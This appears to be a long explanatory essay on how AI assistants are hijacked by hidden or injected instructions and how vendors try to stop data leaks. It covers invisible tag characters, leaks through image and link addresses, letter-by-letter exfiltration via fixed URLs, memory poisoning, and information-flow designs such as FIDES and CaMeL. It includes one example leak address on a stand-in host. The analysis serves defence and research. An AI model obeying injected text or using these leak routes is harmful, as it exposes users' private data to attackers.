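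| Assistant | Tag characters, September 2025 | Variation selectors, January 2026 | Later result with tag characters |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Resisted | Resisted | GPT-5.6 Sol did not obey, 2026 |
| Claude | Resisted | Resisted | Opus 5 warned the user, 2026 |
| Gemini | Vulnerable | Vulnerable | Two newer models obeyed through the API, August 2026 |
| Grok | Vulnerable | Vulnerable on the second attempt | Grok 4.5 obeyed through the API, August 2026 |
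| DeepSeek | Vulnerable | Resisted | None known |
| Copilot | Resisted | Not tested | None known |
| Meta's assistant | Not tested | Resisted | None known |

The last column comes from the classroom experiments by Aiersilan and colleagues. Their API results suggest that neither Google nor xAI, which makes Grok, was deleting tag characters for developers in August 2026. Either company could still delete them in its own app.

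A product that "resisted" hidden text doesn't necessarily filter it, because a model that ignores the text gives the same answer as one that never receives it. Claude is the clearest example. A month before FireTail's comparison, Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer for VS Code Vulnerable to Invisible Prompt Injection* described Claude models following tag characters inside Amazon's programming assistant, although they sometimes refused. Opus 5's later warning suggests that the characters still reached the model, which had learned to treat them as suspicious. Resistance that comes from the model can change with the next model or a different prompt, while deleting the characters would not depend on either.

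### Google's case for leaving it alone

FireTail reported Gemini's behaviour to Google on 18 September 2025 and received a "no action" response. Google's reasons are public only through FireTail. BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability* quotes Google as writing that the attack "can only result in social engineering" (deceiving a person) and that a fix "would not make our users less prone to such attacks".

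Android Authority's *Google says it won't fix Gemini security flaw* (2025) and TechRadar's *Google says it won't fix this potentially concerning Gemini security issue* also report that Google places the responsibility on the user. The words that BGR quotes don't place it there. TechRadar also illustrates the attack with white text in font size zero, a different disguise that a character filter would not remove.

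Google has a point, since anyone who can send Ana a calendar invitation can also lie to her in visible text. But in *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, the FireTail researcher vict0ni demonstrated a lie that would be harder to catch. The calendar showed a harmless event, while Gemini gave the user a false organiser and meeting link taken from hidden text. Ana could inspect such an event and find nothing wrong. Gemini also used the invitation before the user had accepted it.

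The word "only" is harder to defend. In August 2025, Embrace The Red showed hidden text in a bug report instructing Jules, Google's programming agent, to add a function to a program and run it. Jules approved its own plan automatically, so the attacker did not have to deceive anyone. Google had also taken the underlying behaviour more seriously in February 2024, when it accepted Rehberger's first report about Gemini as a valid bug and passed it to the product team. Eighteen months later, the models still followed hidden text.

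### Provider, application or mail system

The case for having the model's provider filter hidden characters is that one change protects every product built on the model, including those whose developers have never heard of tag characters. In August 2025, Embrace The Red reported that OpenAI appeared to be the only vendor to have done this. Graves considers filtering at the tokenizer the most robust defence, because the model then never receives the hidden text.

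However, a provider doesn't know why a customer is sending the characters. A security analyst might want the model to examine a suspicious email, and the teachers in the classroom experiment depended on hidden text reaching the model. Opus 5 also warned the user about the characters, which a model can't do if it never receives them.

Rehberger concluded that developers who build on Claude have to filter out hidden characters themselves, since as far as he knew Anthropic did not intend to change its models. AWS also addresses its advice to application developers, and calls such protections "fundamental components" of critical applications. On 5 July 2025, Rehberger reported that Amazon's own programming assistant lacked such protection. AWS told him by 8 August that it had fixed this, but it issued no public advisory.

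An application's developer knows which text came from a stranger and which languages the users write in. Unlike a mail system, the developer also controls how the answer appears. In Embrace The Red's *Sneaking Invisible Instructions by Developers in Windsurf*, Rehberger would prefer interfaces to show hidden characters, but he thinks deleting them before and after the model runs is probably more practical.

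Microsoft argues that the mail system should remove hidden characters, because cleaning a message on arrival helps both the spam filter and any assistant that uses the message later. Cleaning email doesn't protect web pages or shared documents, though some publishing software may remove the characters there. Language Log reported in 2024 that WordPress, which runs many websites, seemed to delete tag characters from the text it stored.

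These positions are compatible, because running the same filter twice does little harm. A provider could delete tag characters by default and let customers who need them turn the filter off. The application would still have to check the chatbot's answer. Asking users to protect themselves makes the least sense, because they can't see the characters.

### Visible instructions and other disguises

Filtering tag characters is easy enough that a developer has little reason to leave it out, but it solves a small part of the problem. Rehberger himself rates invisible instructions as less severe than an agent's ability to run tools without the user's approval.

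Attackers have other ways to hide text. Oasis Security's *Claudy Day* describes a 2026 attack on claude.ai that hid instructions with HTML. *Hidden-in-Plain-Text* (2026), a benchmark of instructions planted in web content, covers off-screen text, image descriptions and Unicode tricks. Cleaning both the HTML and the Unicode made models follow fewer of these instructions, but the researchers warn that this cleaning may also remove material the assistant needs to find.

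In one attack, invisible instructions made Amp, Sourcegraph's programming agent, search for a secret key, put it in a web address, and open the page or display an image from it. Rehberger advised Sourcegraph to strip the hidden characters, ask users before visiting unfamiliar sites, and close the routes by which data could leave. As far as he could tell, the company only stripped the characters. That stopped the invisible instructions, but visible ones in a file that nobody read closely could still have made Amp send the key to the same address.

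## Restricting the addresses an assistant can load

Amp would open any address the model wrote. Google and OpenAI check addresses before their assistants load them, so a successful injection may still fail to send data out.

### Google's rules for images and links

Gemini doesn't display images from outside servers. In June 2025, the month EchoLeak was disclosed, Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) described a filter that finds external image addresses in the model's Markdown and prevents the images from rendering. Google concluded that EchoLeak's image leak did not apply to Gemini.

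Gemini checks the links in its answers with Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous sites, and replaces only the suspicious ones with the words "suspicious link removed". This should work well against known phishing sites, but an attacker can set up a new server in minutes, and it will have no reputation. Tenable's *The Trifecta* reports that Gemini also sent links through a google.com address and cut suspicious answers short. Tenable got the data out through Gemini's browsing tool, which these measures did not cover.

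*Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes a central policy engine that now holds Google's rules for addresses, user confirmations and sequences of tool calls. Staff can respond to a new attack by changing a setting, which is faster than retraining a model. According to Embrace The Red, Google also uses its search index to decide which addresses Gemini may load without asking. OpenAI has described its version of that check in more detail.

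### Why lists of trusted sites fail

Letting the assistant load addresses only from well-known sites would be simpler, but OpenAI gives two reasons why this isn't enough. First, many well-known sites have addresses that redirect visitors elsewhere, so a check of the first server's name can approve a request that ends at the attacker's server. Second, people visit far more sites than any list could include, so a strict list would produce frequent false alarms, and users would learn to click through them.

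A program can handle redirects by checking every address along the way. A trusted site where strangers can collect data is harder to handle. The email assistant Superhuman AI allowed images from docs.google.com, and Willison (2026) explains that Google Forms, on the same domain, saves data sent to it in a web address. An injected email could therefore make the assistant submit the contents of dozens of private emails to the attacker's Google form, where the attacker could read them. Superhuman treated the report as a high priority and fixed the flaw.

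Google had made a similar assumption in Colab, its online programming notebook. Colab showed a confirmation page before opening a link from Gemini, but Embrace The Red found that it skipped this page for Google's own domains. Those domains host Apps Script, a service where anyone can publish a small program that records the data sent to it.

### OpenAI's public-index rule

The rule that OpenAI published on 28 January 2026 depends on the exact address instead of the site's reputation. It works as follows:

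1. A crawler, which is a program that explores the web as a search engine does, records the public addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. Before ChatGPT opens a page or loads an image on its own, it compares the full address with this record.
3. If the address matches exactly, ChatGPT loads it.
4. If there is no match, ChatGPT either tries a different site or shows a warning that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. The user can still choose to open it.

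Suppose Ana asks about paper prices and ChatGPT tries to open the printing firm's public price list. The crawler has probably recorded that address, so the page loads. If a hostile page then gets the model to write `https://stranger.example/page?note=blue-kettle`, the crawler should have no record of that address, because nobody outside Ana's company knows the code name. Even if the crawler has recorded `https://stranger.example/page`, the added note makes it a different address.

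This works only if the crawler finds addresses independently of conversations. Otherwise, an address containing Ana's data could enter the index and count as public from then on.

Requiring an exact match is much stricter than allowing a list of domains. It would have blocked the Superhuman attack, EchoLeak and SearchLeak, because each put text specific to the victim into an address on a trusted server.

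The rule will also hold up some harmless requests, because a page that tracks Ana's parcel or a document that a colleague shared through a private link is unlikely to be in a public index. Addresses that users supply themselves are exempt. Rehberger writes in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that, as he understands it, ChatGPT treats an address in the user's own message as safe for the rest of that chat.

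This exception assumes that users know what is in their messages, but people often paste text they haven't read closely. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) suggested that ChatGPT could refuse to open any link when the prompt contained pasted text. That would be safer, but ChatGPT then couldn't open an article to summarize it if the user had pasted its address.

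### From the 2023 check to the 2025 changes

OpenAI added ChatGPT's first check, a feature called url_safe, in December 2023. It did not explain how the feature decided whether an address was safe. Rehberger worked out some of the rules by experiment and found ways around them, which he presented at the Black Hat Europe conference in 2024.

One weakness of url_safe was that it allowed any address on certain sites. According to Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, an attacker needed one of these sites, a way to send data to it through a web address, and a way to read what arrived, such as a log file. Rehberger reported several such gaps in October 2024 and was surprised to find some still open in 2025. OpenAI closed them around August 2025, and its January 2026 paper describes the mechanism it had added.

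OpenAI also restricted ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as written. *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026) explains that this blocked an attack called ShadowLeak, because the model could no longer add a name or other private data to an address. The security firm Radware soon showed that ChatGPT could still leak data by opening unaltered addresses.

### Spelling out a secret with fixed addresses

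Radware's *ZombieAgent*, published in January 2026, describes an email that listed a separate web address for each letter and digit. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, ChatGPT read the email, found the private data and opened the addresses in the order that spelled it out. A nine-character name took nine requests, which came from OpenAI's servers, not the user's browser.

Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. Radware says one version of the attack worked 100% of the time, but doesn't say how many times it was tried. The attack was possible a month after the August changes. Unless Radware's pages were already in OpenAI's index, the check either did not yet cover email accounts connected to ChatGPT or was less strict than the rule OpenAI described in January.

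The public-index rule makes this kind of leak harder, because the crawler must already have found the attacker's pages. But Rehberger points out that many ordinary blogs have 36 indexed pages, and he says OpenAI's paper also acknowledges the problem. The addresses contain no private data, but the order in which ChatGPT visits them can reveal some.

The amount is easy to calculate. If the model can choose among N permitted addresses, each request conveys at most

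log₂ N bits

With 36 addresses, each request can carry about 5.2 bits. A six-digit code has a million possible values, or about 19.9 bits, so sending one takes at least four requests. The table gives the minimum for other values of N, assuming the server receives the requests in order.

| Permitted addresses | Bits per request | Requests for a six-digit code | Requests for 300 random letters and digits |
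|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.0 | 20 | 1,551 |
| 10 | 3.3 | 6 | 467 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 4 | 300 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 | 156 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 1 | 78 |

These are theoretical limits. To send a code in four requests, the model would have to convert it to base 36 without a mistake. Sending one digit at a time is simpler and takes six requests.

Without the public-index rule, a single address can carry all 300 characters. With the rule, an attacker with 36 pages needs 300 requests, and one with a million pages still needs 78. The rule therefore protects long documents well, but passwords and sign-in codes much less.

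Limiting the number of requests would reduce the leak further. In 2024, ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which restricted a letter-by-letter attack to ten characters per prompt. That is still enough for a sign-in code, but a 300-character email would take 30 prompts.

Rehberger also suggests that ChatGPT could keep a cached copy of each page for a few minutes, or refuse to open the same address twice in one session. In both cases, the attacker's server would receive only the first visit to each page. An attacker who used one page per digit would therefore miss any repeated digits, which about 85% of six-digit codes contain.

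In principle, though, a ban on repeat visits barely hinders the attacker. There are 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 = 1,413,720 ways to visit four different pages out of 36, still more than the number of possible codes. Radware's researchers had also prepared separate addresses for each position in the text, so that the requests could arrive in any order. The model then never has to visit an address twice, but leaking ten characters takes 360 indexed pages instead of 36. Rehberger expects his proposals to limit the leak without ending it.

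### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* describes a later setting for users who want more protection. It restricts web browsing to cached pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. An attacker who can't see which pages the model opens learns nothing from its choice, however many pages are in the index.

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode is a setting that removes most of the outside communication that the lethal trifecta requires. Willison (2026) writes that it "looks really good to me". OpenAI had announced it in February 2026 and was extending it to personal accounts, including free ones, in June.

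The user gives up a lot in return. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* reports that the setting disables agent mode and deep research, which compiles long reports from many websites. Cached pages are also of little use for checking whether a train is late. OpenAI says most people don't need the setting and does not guarantee that it prevents every leak, since data could still get out through connected apps or an undiscovered method. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* adds that an injection in a cached page or an uploaded file can still affect the answer.

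### Asking the user, or giving the assistant less

A company can also have a person approve risky actions. Gemini, for example, asks for confirmation before it deletes calendar events, and ChatGPT warns about unverified links. But *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) points out that people tire of confirmation requests and that an attacker can trick them into agreeing. If Ana sees 20 warnings each working day and one real attack a year, only about one warning in 5,000 concerns a real attack.

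Even a careful user can't always tell what she is approving. An address from the ZombieAgent attack ends in one letter, and Ana couldn't know that this letter was the third in her password. Approval works better for actions whose effects are visible, such as deleting Saturday's appointments.

Another option is to restrict what the assistant can access at one time. Radware found that once ChatGPT had used a connected service such as Gmail, it could not use its long-term memory in the same chat. This was meant to stop a hostile email from storing instructions there. But ChatGPT could still consult its memory first and then open Gmail. Radware used a shared file to plant a memory that made ChatGPT read the attacker's email whenever the user sent a message, so the attack continued into later conversations. Blocking Gmail after memory use as well would have prevented this, but the assistant could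 not then use the user's saved preferences when reading their mail.

For programming agents, Willison (2025) recommends using passwords and keys from test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a thief gains little by stealing them. This is harder to do with an office assistant, because Ana needs answers from her real mail and contracts.

### Tracking private data through the system

Information-flow control is a more ambitious approach. A program outside the model records where each piece of data came from and who may see it, then uses these records to decide whether to allow an action. The assistant can keep its access to private data, untrusted text and the outside world, but the program prevents dangerous combinations of the three.

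In CaMeL, a design from 2025, one model receives the user's request and writes a plan as a short program. A second model reads emails and web pages but has no tools. The software that runs the plan tracks the origin of every value and checks a policy before each tool call. A hostile email might falsify a summary, but it can't add a step to the plan.

FIDES, designed by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, attaches two labels to each piece of data. One lists the people who may read it, and the other records whether it comes from a trusted source. When the agent combines two pieces, only people who could read both may read the result:

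readers(x and y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

Suppose Ana, Ben and Carla are allowed to read the notes on a contract, and Ana, Ben and the printing firm are allowed to read an email about it. Then only Ana and Ben can read a summary of both. FIDES can send the summary through a channel only if no one except Ana and Ben would receive it, so it can't send the summary to a stranger's server.

A further rule allows an important action only if no untrusted text influenced the decision to take it. In an ordinary agent, this rule would block almost every important action after the agent read its first outside email. FIDES therefore stores untrusted text in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. If Ana asks the agent to summarize three emails and send the summary to Ben on Slack, the planning model has an isolated model write the summary, then sends it to Ben without reading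 it, so nothing in the emails can change the recipient.

Some requests depend on the content, such as "if anyone has asked for a meeting, put it in my calendar". For these, the isolated model can return a yes or no, which gives the stranger one bit of influence over the plan. A choice among N listed tasks gives log₂ N bits, as with the permitted addresses. Costa and colleagues consider an answer this small unlikely to carry an injection.

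The FIDES tests ran in AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The table's last column counts successful attacks, and the other columns show the share of tasks each agent completed when not under attack. The average weights the four environments equally.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no policy | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 84.3% | 152 |
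| Ordinary, with policy | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 41.9% | 0 |
| FIDES, with policy | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 50.0% | 0 |

The policy stopped every attack, and FIDES recovered some of the usefulness that an ordinary agent lost under the policy. But FIDES still completed only half the tasks, compared with 84% for an agent without protection. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, up from 41%, because o1 was better at working with variables. Models have improved greatly since o1, so the gap has probably narrowed further.

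Even with a better model, the policy would block some tasks. Many banking tasks required the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, for instance to make a payment, and the policy is meant to stop the agent from doing this. If Ana wants her assistant to pay emailed invoices as written, she is letting a stranger's text determine what it pays.

The zero leaves out three attacks that AgentDojo's own scoring counted as successful against FIDES with the policy on. Costa and colleagues excluded them after inspection, partly because AgentDojo counts as successful attacks some actions that the policy permits or has already blocked. They also labelled a type of data as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. A company can't know in advance where attacks will appear, so it would have to label more data as untrusted, which would make the assistant less useful, or accept some risk.

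FIDES also doesn't prevent leaks through the agent's choices. If the agent visits one page when a contract exists and another when it doesn't, an observer learns whether the contract exists, even though the agent sent no private text. Costa and colleagues chose not to prevent such leaks because doing so would mean forbidding nearly all outside communication once the agent had read anything private.

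In its basic form, FIDES checks tool calls but treats the final answer to the user as harmless. This is a practical gap for chatbots, because EchoLeak sent data out through an image in the answer. Costa and colleagues note that FIDES can also apply its policies to answers, and any product that displays links or images would need to do this.

CaMeL blocked nearly all AgentDojo attacks while completing about as many tasks as other agents, according to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025). One drawback is that developers must describe the format of each tool's output, because the planning model writes its program before it sees any results. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends the design to groups of agents, found that CaMeL needed these format descriptions to be reasonably useful, and that the standard tool descriptions in two benchmarks left them out. Developers only have to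 add them once for each set of tools, which is a small job.

### Where to put the boundary

Rehberger argues that companies should focus on the output channel, because outside communication is the only part of the lethal trifecta that is "realistically enforceable". The *Silent Egress* results support this, since a list of allowed domains blocked every request, while a warning to the model stopped only a third of them.

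One reason to improve the model itself is that some attacks cause harm without an output channel. Radware also got ChatGPT to alter a medical history in its memory, which led to harmful advice. No data left the system, so a check on addresses would not have stopped the attack. OpenAI similarly acknowledges that its own rule does not ensure that a page's content is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions.

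Model training has also improved resistance to attacks. Google trained Gemini 2.5 on attacks that another system generated automatically, and Gavish reports that this kind of training lowered the success rate of attacks without making Gemini less efficient, though he gives no figures. Anthropic's and OpenAI's published attack success rates for newer models are low. Separate detectors can also work well. Rahman and Kim tested one that flagged every reworded version of their attack and raised no false alarms.

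Those who favour restricting the output channel reply that attackers adapt. According to SecurityWeek, attacks adapted to Gemini 2.0's defences did better in 16 of 24 cases. Instructions to the model can also be fragile. Rahman and Kim cut the leak rate from 31.9% to zero by forbidding the agent to reveal its secret "in any form", but the rate was 48.8% with a version that listed specific forbidden behaviours and left out that phrase.

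Controls on output can also fail, because they are only as reliable as the company's list of routes by which data can leave. After Microsoft blocked images and then links, researchers moved on to fonts, saved files and the code sandbox.

Address checks and model training fail in different ways. Suppose Copilot retrieves 1,000 hostile emails and the model obeys 2% of them. A sound address check prevents all 20 of those injections from sending out a long document, but if the attacker knows a gap in the check, all 20 can. Better training might reduce the 20 to two, which helps most when the check has an undiscovered gap, but one of those two could still cause a serious leak. A guarantee against data theft therefore has to come from the output channel or from information-flow control. Training makes it less likely that an attack reaches those controls, and it is the main protection against false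 answers.

### Defences that some products lack

When OpenAI introduced url_safe, the ChatGPT apps for macOS and iOS did not use it, so it did not protect them. Rehberger thinks some of OpenAI's own developers may not know about the newer check, a problem he has often seen in security work.

Gemini refuses to load outside images, but this did not protect Gemini Enterprise from GeminiJack, an attack that the security firm Noma Labs discovered. According to SC Media, instructions in an email, calendar invitation or shared document made the assistant search for private information and add the results to an image address. The attack ran when an employee did a routine search.

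Antigravity, Google's AI programming tool, could leak data through its browser. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* shows how a web page with programming advice could make the tool steal passwords and source code, despite its default list of permitted sites. Willison noted in November 2025 that Google already listed data exfiltration as a known issue in Antigravity, so researchers could not claim a reward for reporting it. Google said it was working on a fix.

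Microsoft may have the hardest task, because more than 80 of its products now use the Copilot name, and a restriction that works in one may be missing from another.
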